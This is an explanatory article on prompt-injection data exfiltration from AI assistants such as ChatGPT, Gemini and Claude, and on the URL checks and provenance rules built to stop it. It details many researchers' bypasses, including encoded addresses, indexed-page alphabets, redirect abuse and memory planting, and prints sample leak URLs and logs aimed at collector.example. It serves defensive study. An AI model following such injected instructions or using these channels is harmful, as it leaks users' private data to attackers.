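In November 2023 OpenAI began letting customers build their own versions of ChatGPT, called GPTs. Rehberger built one that offered a game of tic-tac-toe but first asked for the player's email address and password, then sent both to his server in the URL of a hidden image. According to Embrace The Red's *Malicious ChatGPT Agents*, he reported it to OpenAI on 13 November, and the company closed the report two days later as "Not Applicable". According to SecurityWeek's *Malicious GPT Can Phish Credentials, Exfiltrate Them to External Server*, he published the demonstration on 12 December. Soon afterwards he ran it live with a volunteer, and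 his server received the conversation. The next day, the ChatGPT website refused to load the image.

### A question before each image

If Dana had used ChatGPT in early 2024, the hijacked model could have written the same line of markdown. But before creating the image, the code of the ChatGPT website would have sent the address to an OpenAI service called url_safe. In simplified form, the exchange would have looked like this:

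```
Question:  url_safe?url=collector.example/logo.png?d=HERON-4417

Answer:    {"safe": false}
```

The website displays the image only if the answer is true. Here it would not have created an image, so Dana's browser would not have contacted collector.example. Sending the address to OpenAI revealed nothing new to the company, because the model's answer had come from OpenAI's servers. Tenable's *HackedGPT* (2025) adds that the service also checked most links, and that ChatGPT left out those that failed the check.

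Unlike a CSP, url_safe could check a URL's query string, so it could allow a site's logo but block the same logo if a door code had been added to its URL. ChatGPT could therefore show images from sites that were not on an OpenAI allowlist.

OpenAI could also log every check, including checks of approved addresses, which a CSP's reports leave out. That would help OpenAI notice a leak that used a series of nearly identical approved addresses. Rehberger welcomed this and hoped a central service would also let companies set stricter rules for their own staff.

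Every app needed its own code for the check, and OpenAI's phone apps, and later its Mac app, at first had none. Rehberger guessed that OpenAI had put the check in the website so that answers could keep streaming, but he thought it belonged on the server, where it would protect every app.

Outsiders also could not read the service's rules, whereas they can read a CSP. But the secrecy gave limited protection. The website had to query the service, so a user could query it too with the browser's developer tools. An attacker could test addresses in advance and keep the ones that passed. Willison called the solution "half-baked" and expected somebody to get past it by hiding data in subdomains or file names.

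### What researchers inferred

Rehberger began testing on the first day. He tried an image address on his own server for each of the 26 letters and ten digits, and ChatGPT displayed the images at nine of the 36. It accepted a.png but not d.png, and he could not tell why. He used the accepted addresses to leak the word "hi" one letter at a time.

Nine addresses are enough to leak a six-digit login code. By the formula in the previous section, a sequence of seven images chosen from those addresses can represent any such code. An attacker could also have tested more file names until every character had an address that passed the check. Rehberger advised OpenAI to display only one image per answer, or a handful at most.

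Two months later, Wu, Zhang and colleagues (2024) had worked out one of the rules. In *A New Era in LLM Security*, they asked ChatGPT to read web pages that requested an image. ChatGPT displayed the image if the page gave a fixed address, but url_safe returned false if the page told ChatGPT to insert a secret into the address first. They concluded that url_safe accepted any address that had already appeared in the conversation, whether in the user's message or in text from a plugin (an add-on that connected ChatGPT to another service).

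The rule makes sense because an address that a stranger wrote in advance can't contain a secret the model has only just read. But url_safe apparently checked only whether the address was in the conversation, not who had composed it. Wu and colleagues exploited this with a plugin that created online documents. Their malicious page had ChatGPT save the chat history in one document, put that document's link into an image address, and save the address in a second document. When ChatGPT read the second document back, the image address became part of the conversation and passed the check. The attacker received the link and could use it to open the chat history, whatever its length.

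The attack succeeded with all eight web-reading plugins the researchers tried, though they do not report how many attempts each one took. It also required the document plugin. Rehberger notes that OpenAI later removed plugins from ChatGPT. Wu and colleagues reported the flaws to OpenAI, but they do not say when they did so, whether OpenAI replied, or whether it fixed them.

The security company Imperva tested url_safe directly. Imperva's *From ChatBot To SpyBot*, published soon after ChatGPT gained its memory feature, concludes that the service was essentially a text search. It returned true for any string, even one that was not a valid address, that appeared anywhere in the text the user had supplied, including the custom instructions that ChatGPT applies to every conversation.

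Imperva also tested addresses that were not in the conversation and found that some of them passed:

| Address not yet in the conversation | Result |
|---|---|
| An ordinary domain with nothing after it | Safe |
| A subdomain of an ordinary domain | Not safe |
| An ordinary domain followed by a path or query string | Not safe |
| A subdomain of google.com | Safe |
| Any subdomain, path or query string on openai.com | Safe |

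The second row makes sense because a domain's owner can create any number of subdomains for free and put data in their names. An attacker can also use whole domains to carry data, but has to buy each one. Imperva put the price at $1 to $2 per domain, so buying one for every letter and digit would cost $36 to $72.

An easier method was to use the custom instructions, which hold 3,000 characters, to list an address for each character. To save space, an attacker could list one long address and have ChatGPT cut it off at a different point for each character, because the text search also accepted part of an address. In Imperva's scenario, the attacker had already broken into the account through another flaw. The planted instructions would then keep leaking data after the stolen login expired.

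Imperva still thought OpenAI was moving in the right direction, because extracting large amounts of data consistently without detection had become much harder. Imperva does not mention reporting these methods to OpenAI or any fix for them.

### Leaking data by choosing an address

In *Exfiltration of personal information from ChatGPT via prompt injection* (June 2024), Schwartzman used the same weakness to leak data through ChatGPT's browsing tool, which opened only addresses that appeared in the prompt. He hid his instructions in a long piece of code that a user might paste into ChatGPT with a question about it.

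The first version of the attack listed six addresses, one for each ten-year age range up to 60, and had ChatGPT open the one that matched the user. All six were in the prompt, so ChatGPT was allowed to open any of them, and its choice revealed the user's age range to the server's owner. ChatGPT could infer the range from a remark about finishing school or retiring soon, without knowing the user's exact age.

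This method can't handle a postal code, which has too many possible values to list. Schwartzman's second version relied on ChatGPT also accepting shortened forms of a listed address. Suppose the prompt contains this one:

```
collector.example/send/abcdefghij
```

If ChatGPT opens the address only as far as the "a", that means 0, stopping at "b" means 1, and opening the whole address means 9, so a single line of text can represent any digit. ChatGPT would not open the same address twice, which Schwartzman attributed to caching, so he supplied ten different lines, one for each position in the number. These replaced 100 separate addresses.

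ChatGPT made mistakes when it had to shorten the addresses itself, so the instructions included a short Python program to do the counting. At the time, ChatGPT opened at most ten addresses per prompt, which limited the leak to ten digits, or about 33 bits. Schwartzman published videos of both versions working but no success rates. The second version was slow enough for a user to notice and stop it. ChatGPT also showed a small box that the user could click to see the opened address, but the data had already been sent by then.

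Schwartzman demonstrated the attack only with the browsing tool. Rehberger pointed out to him that the same techniques could be used with images.

Schwartzman expected that OpenAI could add a check that compares whole addresses. This would have prevented the shortening trick but not the first version, in which ChatGPT opened a listed address exactly as written. CamoLeak's signed pictures leaked data in the same way as the first version.

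Schwartzman reported the problem to OpenAI through Bugcrowd, but the report was marked "not applicable". MITRE declined to list the problem in the public catalogue of vulnerabilities because ChatGPT is a web application that customers do not control. Japan's IPA, a government-backed technology agency, replied that it could do nothing because OpenAI's terms made users responsible for what they put into ChatGPT and what came out. Schwartzman then published the attack without a fix in place. He suggested that ChatGPT ask before opening any link, or refuse to open links when a prompt contained pasted text.

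### The Bing redirects

Some domains passed the check regardless of the conversation. One was bing.com, according to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass*. Bing's search results link to bing.com addresses that redirect to the chosen site, so every site in Bing's index had a link that url_safe would accept. Tenable's researchers got their own test sites indexed and copied the redirect links.

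Nobody could alter these links, so the model couldn't add a secret to them. Tenable instead had Bing index a page for each letter of the alphabet, and ChatGPT spelled out the stolen words by displaying the matching links as images.

In this attack, url_safe approved the Bing address, and the browser then followed the redirect to Tenable's server without another check. A CSP would have blocked the redirect unless it also allowed that server.

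Getting at private data took more work because ChatGPT passed web browsing to a second model that could not see the user's memories or conversation. Tenable calls this model SearchGPT. A malicious comment under a blog post could hijack SearchGPT, and Tenable had the hijacked model end its summary with instructions for ChatGPT. When the user sent another message, ChatGPT read the summary as part of the conversation and followed the instructions.

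A display bug hid them from the user. When a summary contained a code block, the website left out any text after the first word on the block's opening line, but ChatGPT could still read it. Tenable also used SearchGPT's output to make ChatGPT save a memory that would cause it to leak data in every later conversation.

Tenable reported the Bing bypass on 10 December 2024, and OpenAI acknowledged it the same day. On 3 January 2025 OpenAI added another person to the correspondence. Tenable asked for an update five more times, the last on 4 March, and its timeline shows no reply. Tenable published the advisory while the flaw was still unfixed.

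In November 2025 Tenable wrote that it had worked with OpenAI to fix some of the seven problems it had found in ChatGPT, but did not say whether the Bing bypass was one of them. The attack through a blog comment also worked on ChatGPT 5, which OpenAI released in August 2025, so the redirects evidently still worked months after the advisory.

### Approved sites with readable logs

Rehberger had found a way to leak much more data per image. Embrace The Red's *AI Domination*, which describes part of his 2024 Black Hat Europe talk, lists three requirements: url_safe must accept the site, the site must accept data in an ordinary web request, and the attacker must be able to read what the site received.

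GitHub met only the first two. Rehberger could post new instructions there for a hijacked ChatGPT to fetch, but only GitHub's owner, Microsoft, could read the server logs. Microsoft's Azure cloud service met all three, because it rents out file storage at addresses under windows.net, which url_safe accepted, and lets customers see a log of requests for their files. Rehberger opened a storage account and had ChatGPT add private data to an address there.

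Google had made the same mistake with Bard's CSP in 2023. In ChatGPT, the mistake also removed the main limit on the earlier attacks against url_safe. Those attacks used a fixed address for each character, so ChatGPT needed one image per character. On windows.net, it could put a whole passage of text into a single address. url_safe received the query string and could have refused such addresses, but it evidently allowed any query string on this domain.

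Rehberger reported this bypass and several others in early October 2024. In 2025 he found that some still worked. By then an attacker could steal more, because ChatGPT had begun to include material from the user's past conversations in its system prompt. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* shows how a malicious PDF could make ChatGPT copy this material into the address of an image on Rehberger's storage account.

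He had also found logs on apache.org that he could read. He recommended that OpenAI publish the list of approved domains and let business customers adjust it. Before publishing the new attack, he asked OpenAI about a fix several times over a month but received no update, so he left out the text of the injection.

In the summer of 2025, Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* demonstrated a leak through the same Azure service. The attack targeted Connectors, a feature that lets ChatGPT search services such as Google Drive. When a user uploaded a document with hidden instructions and asked for a summary, ChatGPT searched the user's Drive for access keys. The researchers first tried an image address on an ordinary testing service, but url_safe refused it. When they switched to an image in their own Azure storage, ChatGPT displayed it and the keys appeared in their log.

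OpenAI responded faster this time. The Decoder's *An invisible prompt in a Google Doc made ChatGPT access data* says OpenAI quickly patched the specific attack Zenity had presented at the Black Hat conference, but gives no date for the patch. It also says the attack could extract only small amounts of data, not entire documents.

### The changes of summer 2025

By then OpenAI had changed the check at least once. In April 2025 Tenable reported that a link to ChatGPT could contain a request, which ChatGPT submitted as soon as the user clicked the link. The later RovoBlast attack on Atlassian worked in much the same way. According to the timeline in *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (Tenable, 2025), OpenAI's first fix reached all users on 30 April but did not solve the problem. On 11 July OpenAI said it had added protection against automatic submission and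 improved the behaviour of "safe_url", presumably the same service as url_safe.

Rehberger dates a larger change to about August 2025, about ten months after his report. In a later post on Embrace The Red, he writes that additional protections stopped the attacks he had shown at Black Hat and in his posts that summer. He also no longer saw any requests to url_safe in the browser. OpenAI had probably moved the check to its own servers, as he had suggested in 2023. This also made it harder for outsiders to test addresses the way Imperva had.

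OpenAI first explained the new rule in January 2026, in *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link*. ChatGPT now loads an address automatically only if OpenAI's web crawler has already recorded that exact address, however well known the site is. OpenAI gave redirects as one reason not to rely on a list of trusted sites.

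## Approving an address by where it came from

OpenAI's index can include collector.example as easily as a national newspaper, because recording an address involves no judgement about its site. The check works because the crawler, the program that collects the addresses, has no access to anyone's conversations, accounts or personal data. An address it recorded last month can't contain a door code that ChatGPT found in Dana's mailbox this morning, unless somebody had already published that exact address with the code in it.

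Google uses a different test for the same purpose in Gemini. Its software keeps a record, known as URL provenance, of whether an address came unchanged from the user or a data source, or the model composed it. This matters because a model that has read Dana's mailbox could put her door code in an address it composes, which a stranger who wrote the address before the conversation began could not have done.

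### Looking up the exact address

Suppose the hidden text in Dana's price list makes ChatGPT write the image address with her door code after the question mark. Before the image can load, OpenAI's software looks for that exact address in the index. The index may contain collector.example/logo.png, but the version with the door code is new, so ChatGPT does not load the image.

OpenAI treats an address without a match as unverified. ChatGPT then either has the agent (the model working through a task by itself) try a different website or warns the user before opening the address.

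The check would have stopped Rehberger's attack through Azure storage, because no crawler would have recorded an address that contained the user's private text.

An exact match also blocks the most harmful use of a redirect, in which the model writes a trusted site's address followed by a destination that contains the stolen data. The index contains the trusted site but not this full address. But the index may also contain fixed redirect links, like the ones Tenable copied from Bing, and the model could still leak data by choosing between several of them. OpenAI's post does not say whether ChatGPT also looks up the address that a redirect leads to.

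Rehberger writes on Embrace The Red that, as he understands it, ChatGPT also accepts any address the user enters directly in a message, and does so for the rest of that chat. This spares Dana a warning about a page she asked ChatGPT to read. But people also paste in text written by strangers, as in Samoilenko's and Schwartzman's attacks, and any addresses in that text arrive as part of the user's message.

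### Recording who wrote the address

According to Google's Bug Hunters post on Gemini, its provenance rule allows an address that appeared in the user's message or in the data Gemini retrieved, and blocks one that the model composed, with exceptions for spelling corrections and well-known sites. The rule matters mainly for links, because Gemini does not display external images at all.

Google's other link check, based on Safe Browsing, can miss a link that sends private data to a newly registered domain. The domain's age doesn't matter under the provenance rule, because Gemini composed the address.

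The software also doesn't have to distinguish stolen data from an order number, because it only checks whether the address was already in one of the sources.

### Five addresses under both rules

The table shows how the two rules would treat five addresses that might come up in Dana's conversation.

| Address | OpenAI's public-index check | Google's provenance rule |
|---|---|---|
| The attacker's image address with the door code added | Not in the index, so a warning or another site | Composed by the model, so blocked |
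| A public article found by a web search | Loads if the crawler has recorded it | Came from a data source, so allowed |
| A private document link in one of Dana's emails | Not in the index, so a warning | Came from a data source, so allowed |
| A supplier's address that Dana mistyped and the model corrected | Loads if the corrected address is in the index | Composed by the model, but allowed as a correction |
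| A list of addresses prepared by the attacker | Loads only those that the crawler has recorded | Came from a data source, so allowed |

Both rules block the door code, but the provenance rule requires software to track what the model has written. In 2024, Wu and colleagues got past url_safe by having ChatGPT save an image address in an online document and then read it back. If Gemini could do the same with a file in Dana's storage, the address would appear to come from a data source, so Google's software would have to record that Gemini had written the file. The public-index check avoids this problem because the crawler never reads Dana's files.

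The difference is less obvious for the public article. OpenAI's index may not include an article published ten minutes ago. It may also lack an old article's address if that address ends in a code identifying the newsletter it came from, because the check compares the whole address. Google's rule allows both addresses if they came from the search results. The model may also reproduce the address of a useful page from its training without searching. OpenAI's check allows that address if it is in the index, while Google's rule treats it as the model's own composition.

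The main inconvenience of a public index is that it can cause warnings about good links, such as the one to Dana's private document. Companies often share a file through a long, unguessable address that opens it for anyone who has the link. A crawler should never have seen this address, so Dana would get a warning, even though she needs ChatGPT to show her the link and opening it tells the file's host nothing new.

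Crawlers sometimes find links that give the public direct access to a private object, such as an invoice whose address includes its access code, and such links appear in collections of public addresses. *The Silent Spill* (2026) calls this kind of exposure a URL leak. A match in the index therefore proves only that an address was public before the conversation, not that its owner wanted it to be.

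An attacker may also want to steal a private link. In May 2026, Willison described an attack on Microsoft's Copilot Cowork, an agent for office tasks. The attack could leak OneDrive links that let anyone download the files without signing in. If a hijacked model puts such a link inside an address on the attacker's server, the combined address is new, so both rules should block it.

### What the exceptions allow

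Google's rule needs an exception for spelling corrections, because a strict provenance rule would block helpful corrections along with leaks. However, a hijacked model could use that exception to make "corrections" that carry data. OpenAI's rule needs no such exception, because it doesn't depend on who wrote the address.

The more the model may change an address, the more data the address can carry. Suppose the software accepted a change to any one of the last 20 characters, and each could be replaced by any of 35 other letters and digits. The model could then write 20 × 35 = 700 altered addresses. Counting the original, it would have 701 to choose from, and that choice can carry about 9.5 bits, almost enough for two characters of a password. Google could avoid this by accepting a correction only when the resulting address is already in its search index.

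The exception for well-known sites lets Gemini suggest an address such as an encyclopaedia's home page without first finding it in a search. A home page's address can't contain a secret, but if the exception covers every address on a site, an attacker may find a part of the site that collects data. Google's Colab assistant had this problem because its confirmation page exempted Google's own domains, and Embrace The Red used that exemption to get data out through a link.

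A more recent case involved Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office tasks. It could contact only approved domains, including the one that programs use to reach Anthropic's services. According to Willison's *30 posts tagged “lethal-trifecta”*, PromptArmor had the agent upload the user's files to that domain with the attacker's access key instead of the user's. The attacker could then collect the files from an ordinary Anthropic account. Even Anthropic's own domain could be used to take files, which is a good argument for approving individual pages rather than whole domains.

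### ZombieAgent and lists of prepared addresses

The last row of the table describes an attack that researchers carried out on ChatGPT. In June 2025 the security company Radware reported a leak called ShadowLeak, and on 3 September OpenAI told Radware that it had fixed the leak. ChatGPT would now open an address only as it had received it, with nothing added. This was a simple provenance rule.

Radware bypassed this defense within a month. Its paper *ZombieAgent* describes an email containing a separate address for every letter and digit, plus one for a space. When the user asked ChatGPT to do something with their Gmail account, it read the email, found the private data the attacker wanted, and opened the matching addresses one after another, each exactly as it appeared in the email. OpenAI's servers made the requests, so the data left before the user saw an answer.

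Requests might arrive out of order, so Radware also prepared numbered versions of each address, one for each position in the text. Ten characters then required 360 addresses, not counting spaces. Radware reported a 100% success rate for the improved version but did not say how many attempts that covered. Radware also leaked data through markdown images in the user's browser, but found this method less reliable and easier to block.

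Another OpenAI rule prevented ChatGPT from opening a stranger's address that it had stored in its memory. Radware got around this by storing an instruction instead, which made ChatGPT read the attacker's email before answering each new message. ChatGPT then took the addresses from the email, where the rule did not apply. ChatGPT also could not use its memory after reading from a connected service such as Gmail, but it could read its memory first and then the email.

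Radware reported ZombieAgent on 26 September 2025 and OpenAI fixed it on 16 December. According to the news article *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only if it appears in a well-known public index or the user supplied it in the chat. According to the article, the flaw existed because OpenAI hadn't stopped ChatGPT from adding a single letter to an address. Radware's account doesn't support this, since ChatGPT added nothing to the addresses, which the attacker had written out in full.

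The fix forces an attacker to get the addresses into the index first, which is not a large obstacle. Crawlers are built to find public pages, and Tenable (2025) had already got its own test sites into Bing's index for an attack on url_safe. Rehberger points out that anyone with a reasonably large blog probably has 36 indexed pages already. The attacker's email would only have to assign a letter or digit to each page. The pages could be ordinary gardening articles with nothing suspicious in their addresses.

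An attacker could also assign a different word or group of characters to each of thousands of pages. By the formula for image proxies, a choice among 4,096 pages carries 12 bits, so a random 240-bit key would take 20 ordered requests instead of the 47 needed with 36 pages. But the model would have to follow a much longer table without mistakes, and the attacker would have to fit that table into an email or web page.

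The public-index check guarantees that no single address contains a secret from the conversation. But the owner of a group of indexed pages can still learn something from which of them ChatGPT opens. Rehberger described this method in 2023, and he says OpenAI's technical paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*, acknowledges it.

### Links inside pages that Claude fetched

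Anthropic's rule for Claude was stricter than the one ZombieAgent defeated. Claude's tool for reading web pages, web_fetch, could open only an exact address that the user had entered or that Claude's search tool had returned. This design had impressed Willison (2026) because it blocks a request to add private data to an address, whatever the model decides.

The rule had a gap, because Claude could also open links it found on pages it had already fetched. On 9 July 2026 the researcher Ayush Paul published an attack that used this gap to extract what Claude remembered about a user. He built a website for a fictional coffee shop. When Claude visited, the site showed it a false notice that persuaded it to look for the user's profile one letter at a time. The site showed this notice only to programs that identified themselves as Claude.

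Paul's server created the pages as Claude requested them. The opening page had a link for each letter. If Claude opened the link for "a", the next page had links for "aa", "ab", "ac" and so on. White Cloud Security reproduces the path, which grew from "a" to "ay" to "ayu" until it spelled Paul's full name. Paul obtained his home city and his employer's name the same way.

By the last step, Claude was opening an address that contained the user's whole name, although it had not written any of the addresses itself. Paul's server had written them, using letters that Claude's earlier choices had revealed. Anthropic's rule treated all the links alike, although those on the later pages could contain private information and those on the opening page could not.

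This method needs much less preparation than a list. Covering every sequence of ten letters and digits would take 36^10 final addresses, or about 3.7 quadrillion, but the server has to create only the pages that Claude visits. A public-index check would block most of the addresses, because no crawler could record more than a tiny fraction of them. It would still allow the first levels if a crawler had followed the links that far.

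Anthropic confirmed the flaw through HackerOne, a platform that handles security reports. It paid no reward, saying it had already found the problem internally. It then stopped web_fetch from following links in the pages it fetches. Claude can no longer open the sources linked in a report unless the user or the search tool supplies their addresses.

The blog post *The Read-Only Lie* argues that Anthropic closed one channel without changing the condition that made it possible. Paul's attack used only ordinary requests to read pages, and every such request reveals to the server which page the reader wanted. An attacker could still try to get a set of pages into Claude's search results and have Claude choose among them, though this would take much longer to set up than a coffee shop website whose pages appear on demand.

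### What a user can judge from the warning

When ChatGPT can't find an address in the index, it may leave the decision to the user. The dialog in OpenAI's post is titled "Check this link is safe" and includes a warning that ChatGPT has not verified the link and that opening it may share data from the conversation with another site. The dialog shows the address, and the user can copy the link or open it. OpenAI advises anyone who is unsure not to open the link and to ask ChatGPT for a different source or a summary instead.

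This is more useful than a general notice that the user is leaving the site, because it tells people what could go wrong. If Dana saw her door code in the address, she would probably recognise it. An attacker can prevent this by having the model encode the code first. One of these addresses contains HERON-4417 and the other contains a harmless label, "Chair-2026", both in a common encoding called Base64:

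```
collector.example/logo.png?d=SEVST04tNDQxNw

newsletter.example/open?id=Q2hhaXItMjAyNg
```

Dana has no practical way to tell which is which. She can judge whether she recognises the site and whether she expected a link there, but an attacker posing as a supplier can make the site seem familiar and the link seem expected. Copying the link and pasting it into her browser is no safer than opening it.

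OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (March 2026) describes a more helpful version. ChatGPT either shows the user the information it would send and asks for confirmation, or blocks the request and tells the agent to find another way. If the dialog showed "HERON-4417" in plain text, Dana could make an informed decision. But the software would first have to recognise the code inside the address, which is hard for the same reason it is hard for Dana. Blocking the request avoids this problem and works even when nobody is watching the agent.

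When OpenAI explained why it rejected a strict list of approved sites, it wrote that too many false alarms can train people to click through warnings without thinking. The public-index check should cause fewer false alarms on the open web, but it can still cause them for private documents, new pages and personalised links, which office workers open all day.

Anthropic has since published evidence that users often fail to refuse dangerous requests. While 1,053 paid developers worked with its coding agent, Anthropic replaced one of the agent's permission requests with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the developers refused it. The result suited Anthropic, which was arguing for a mode in which software approves most actions instead of the user. A coding agent also asks for permission much more often than ChatGPT warns about links. But the address in a ChatGPT warning usually won't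 be as obviously dangerous as the command in the study.

A missing warning can also mislead people. ChatGPT opens indexed pages without any dialog, even if an attacker is using them. The check verifies only that an address is already public, and OpenAI says the check doesn't guarantee that a page is trustworthy or free of harmful instructions.

### Refusing repeat visits

Rehberger considers the public-index check a significant improvement that makes attacks more complex but doesn't solve the problem. He proposes storing each response for a few minutes, or refusing a second visit to the same address, which would make it harder for an attacker to reuse addresses.

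Storing the response and refusing a second visit would both hide repeated letters and digits from an attacker who uses one page per character, as a strict image cache would. Storing the response is less disruptive because the agent can still reread a page. If Dana asked the agent whether a delivery had moved since the morning, refusing a second visit would stop it from checking, and a stored copy could be out of date if ChatGPT had kept it for too long.

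ChatGPT may already block some repeat visits to the same address, since its browsing tool refused them when Schwartzman tested it in 2024. Rehberger had not tested whether the current version does. Radware's numbered addresses would get around such a limit, as Schwartzman's separate sets of addresses did. The limit would not have affected Paul's coffee shop addresses, because each was one letter longer than the last.

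The proposal is more useful when combined with the public-index check. An attacker who can repeat visits needs 36 indexed pages to send text of any length. Without repeats, ten characters in any order require 360 indexed pages, and 40 characters require 1,440. The owner of a large website may have that many, but someone with a newly registered domain probably does not.

OpenAI could go further by giving the agent the copy of a page that its crawler had already stored. Opening the page would then send no request to its owner, so the agent's choice of page would reveal nothing. But prices, timetables and news would often be out of date. ChatGPT's optional Lockdown Mode, which OpenAI released to personal accounts in June 2026, may work partly like this. OpenAI describes it on its help page as limiting outbound requests, and mentions "cached web content" as a place where hidden instructions could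 still appear.

Willison liked Lockdown Mode because its limits do not depend on an AI model's judgement. He also inferred from it that ChatGPT's default settings do not reliably stop a determined attacker. Dane Stuckey, OpenAI's head of information security, said the mode was not meant for everyone but was worth the loss of features for people who face higher risk because of who they are or what data they handle.

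### Every feature has to use the check

Rehberger's last concern is that OpenAI's own developers may add a feature to ChatGPT without knowing that the url_safe check exists, or without realising that the feature loads addresses. He writes that he often met this problem in his own security work, and that a company can have a good defence that some of its teams don't use. The check was missing from ChatGPT's phone and Mac apps for a similar reason.

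By March 2026, OpenAI had extended the check beyond images in a chat to the pages and bookmarks that the agent opens in Atlas, OpenAI's web browser, and to the searches and page visits of Deep Research, a feature that compiles long reports. Canvas and ChatGPT Apps, in which the model can create and run small programs, instead run them in an isolated environment that detects unexpected communication and asks the user for consent.

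Searches belong on that list because a search tool can also make requests to outside sites. In September 2025 the researcher Abi Raghuram hid instructions in a PDF that got an agent in Notion, a program for notes and shared documents, to collect details of a company's clients. The agent put them into a web address and entered it as a search query. Notion's search tool accepted addresses as well as search terms, so the details reached the server at that address. Willison suggested that Notion stop its search tool from accepting addresses.

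Google had a similar gap in 2025, when Tenable extracted data through Gemini's browsing tool. Tenable's *Gemini Browsing Tool* describes how a hidden instruction made Gemini put the user's saved information and location into an address, then visit it without asking for confirmation. A provenance rule would have identified the address as one the model had composed, but only if the browsing tool had applied the rule. Google has since blocked this leak.

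Even Lockdown Mode worked only if every component followed its restrictions. In November 2026, The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* reported that a flaw in ChatGPT's preview of HTML pages had let specially written content send chat data out despite those restrictions. OpenAI has patched the flaw.

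## Mobile apps, desktop apps and messaging previews

When url_safe appeared in December 2023, only ChatGPT's website used it. The iPhone app received the same answers, including images, but displayed them with its own code, which never contacted url_safe. Rehberger checked version 1.2023.347 of the app at the time and found it still vulnerable to his original attack.

The service could not stop an app from loading an image. An app that never contacted the service displayed every image as before, with no error that might have alerted its developers. Users can also open their ChatGPT conversations on all their devices. If OpenAI stored answers exactly as the model wrote them, Dana could have read the summary of her price list safely on the website, then leaked the door code by opening the same conversation on her phone.

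A CSP has a similar limit because the browser enforces it. It can protect a web page or a desktop program that displays web pages, but not a phone app that draws its own text and pictures, because such an app loads images without checking the website's policy.

### SpAIware

Rehberger warned in 2023 that each app would need its own fix. The next year, OpenAI released a ChatGPT app for the Mac, again without the check. Embrace The Red's *Spyware Injection Into Your ChatGPT's Long-Term Memory (SpAIware)* adds that the Android app also lacked the check, and describes an attack on the Mac app that made the leak permanent.

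The attack used ChatGPT's memory, which saves information about a user and adds it to the prompt in later conversations. In the demonstration, the user had ChatGPT read a web page containing hidden instructions. These made ChatGPT save an instruction in its memory to add an image to its future answers, with the conversation in the image's address. The user then chatted about other things. Each answer included an invisible image, and loading it sent both the user's messages and ChatGPT's replies to Rehberger's server.

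Samoilenko's 2023 attack had also added an image to every answer, but the user could stop it by starting a new conversation. SpAIware continued in new conversations until the user found and deleted the memory. Memories belong to the account, so a page that somebody read while using the protected website could presumably have planted a memory that later leaked data on the Mac.

In May 2024 Rehberger reported that a web page could plant memories in ChatGPT, and OpenAI closed the report as a model safety issue, not a security concern. He reported the complete attack in June. His hidden instructions stopped working in July, but he found a workaround. OpenAI fixed the leak in September in version 1.2024.247, which Mac app users had to install, and Rehberger presented the attack at a security conference on 20 September. The post doesn't include a separate date for the phone apps.

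The update closed the image leak but did not stop web pages from planting memories. Rehberger therefore advised users to review their saved memories regularly and delete any they didn't recognise. An attacker could still plant a memory that used one of the ways around url_safe, as Tenable's later attack did.

### Checking on the server or in each app

If OpenAI's servers had removed unsafe images before sending the answer, as Google's do for Gemini, none of the apps could have loaded them. A check on the server also protects people who never install updates, and it covers the vendor's future apps.

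Streaming makes such a check harder to build, because a server can't take back text it has already sent. The server has to hold back each image until its address passes. Copilot instead cleaned up the answer after it was finished, a mistake that Taler exploited in SearchLeak. For a reference-style image, the server only needs to hold back the line that defines the address. It can send the label immediately, because a label without an address appears as plain text.

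A check in the app is still useful because the server works on text, and apps may handle the same text differently. One app might turn a bare address into a link, and another might fetch a thumbnail for it. But the app's check can be much simpler than url_safe. If the vendor sends all images through its own proxy, each app needs only a rule that blocks images from any other host. An image that the server missed would then leave a blank space. If one app's developers forgot the rule, the server's check would still cover most cases.

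The server should also recheck old answers when it sends them to a newly opened app. Otherwise the app could load an image that the server approved under older rules but would now block.

### Whose server fetches a link preview

Many people use assistants inside Slack, Telegram, Discord or Microsoft Teams, where the assistant's developer controls neither the server that delivers the answer nor the app that displays it. These services show a preview of a linked page, usually with its title, a short description and a picture. Fetching the page to build this preview is called unfurling.

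Suppose Dana asks an assistant in her company's Slack to summarise the price list. Slack passes her message to the assistant's developer, whose software runs the model. The hijacked model adds a link to collector.example with the door code in the address, and the software posts the answer to Slack. Slack's server finds the link and requests the page. The attacker's log gains a line like this:

```
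2026-11-09 10:14:07  198.51.100.7  GET /prices?d=HERON-4417  200
                     "Slackbot-LinkExpanding 1.0"
```

The network address belongs to Slack, and the name at the end identifies the program that made the request. As with an image proxy, the attacker gets the door code but not Dana's network address. Her company's firewall can't block the request, because the request never passes through the company's network. Deleting the message afterwards doesn't undo the leak.

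In Slack, a link that contains the code leaks it before Dana has read the assistant's answer, because Slack fetches the link to build a preview. A developer who has removed every image from the assistant's answers may have left links alone because, in the developer's own chat window, they need a click.

Security researchers knew about these requests early on. Embrace The Red's list of chat apps that fetch links includes a server log entry from Discord's preview program dated 7 April 2023, the day before Rehberger reported the image leak in Bing Chat. But the risk was easy to overlook. Willison had been writing about prompt injection for two years when Rehberger published advice on the risk in August 2024, yet Willison (2024) wrote that he had not thought of this way of leaking data before.

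### PromptArmor's tests of agents and messaging apps

In February 2026 PromptArmor invited the public to test which combinations of agent and messaging app leak data like this. *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* describes the company's website, AITextRisk.com, which recorded every preview request and any data in the requested URL. People tried their own agents, looked for the resulting entry in the log, and reported which agent and app had produced it. They could also report combinations that produced no request.

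PromptArmor singled out OpenClaw on Telegram. OpenClaw is a free agent that people run on their own computers and instruct through messaging apps, and with its default Telegram settings it was exposed. Wondrasek (2026), in *The Agentic Browser Attack Surface You Are Not Thinking About*, lists other combinations from PromptArmor's data:

| Agent | Messaging app | Reported result |
|---|---|---|
| Agents made with Microsoft's Copilot Studio | Teams | At risk |
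| OpenClaw | Telegram | At risk |
| OpenClaw | Discord | At risk |
| Cursor's Slackbot | Slack | At risk |
| Claude app | Slack | Safer |
| OpenClaw | WhatsApp | Safer |
| OpenClaw in an isolated container | Signal | Safer |

The two Slack results suggest that the agent's developer can prevent the leak, since Slack is the same in both. The OpenClaw results suggest that the messaging app matters too. In WhatsApp and Signal, the sender's own app normally builds the preview, so the service's servers don't need to fetch a link that OpenClaw posts. That may explain why volunteers saw no requests in those apps.

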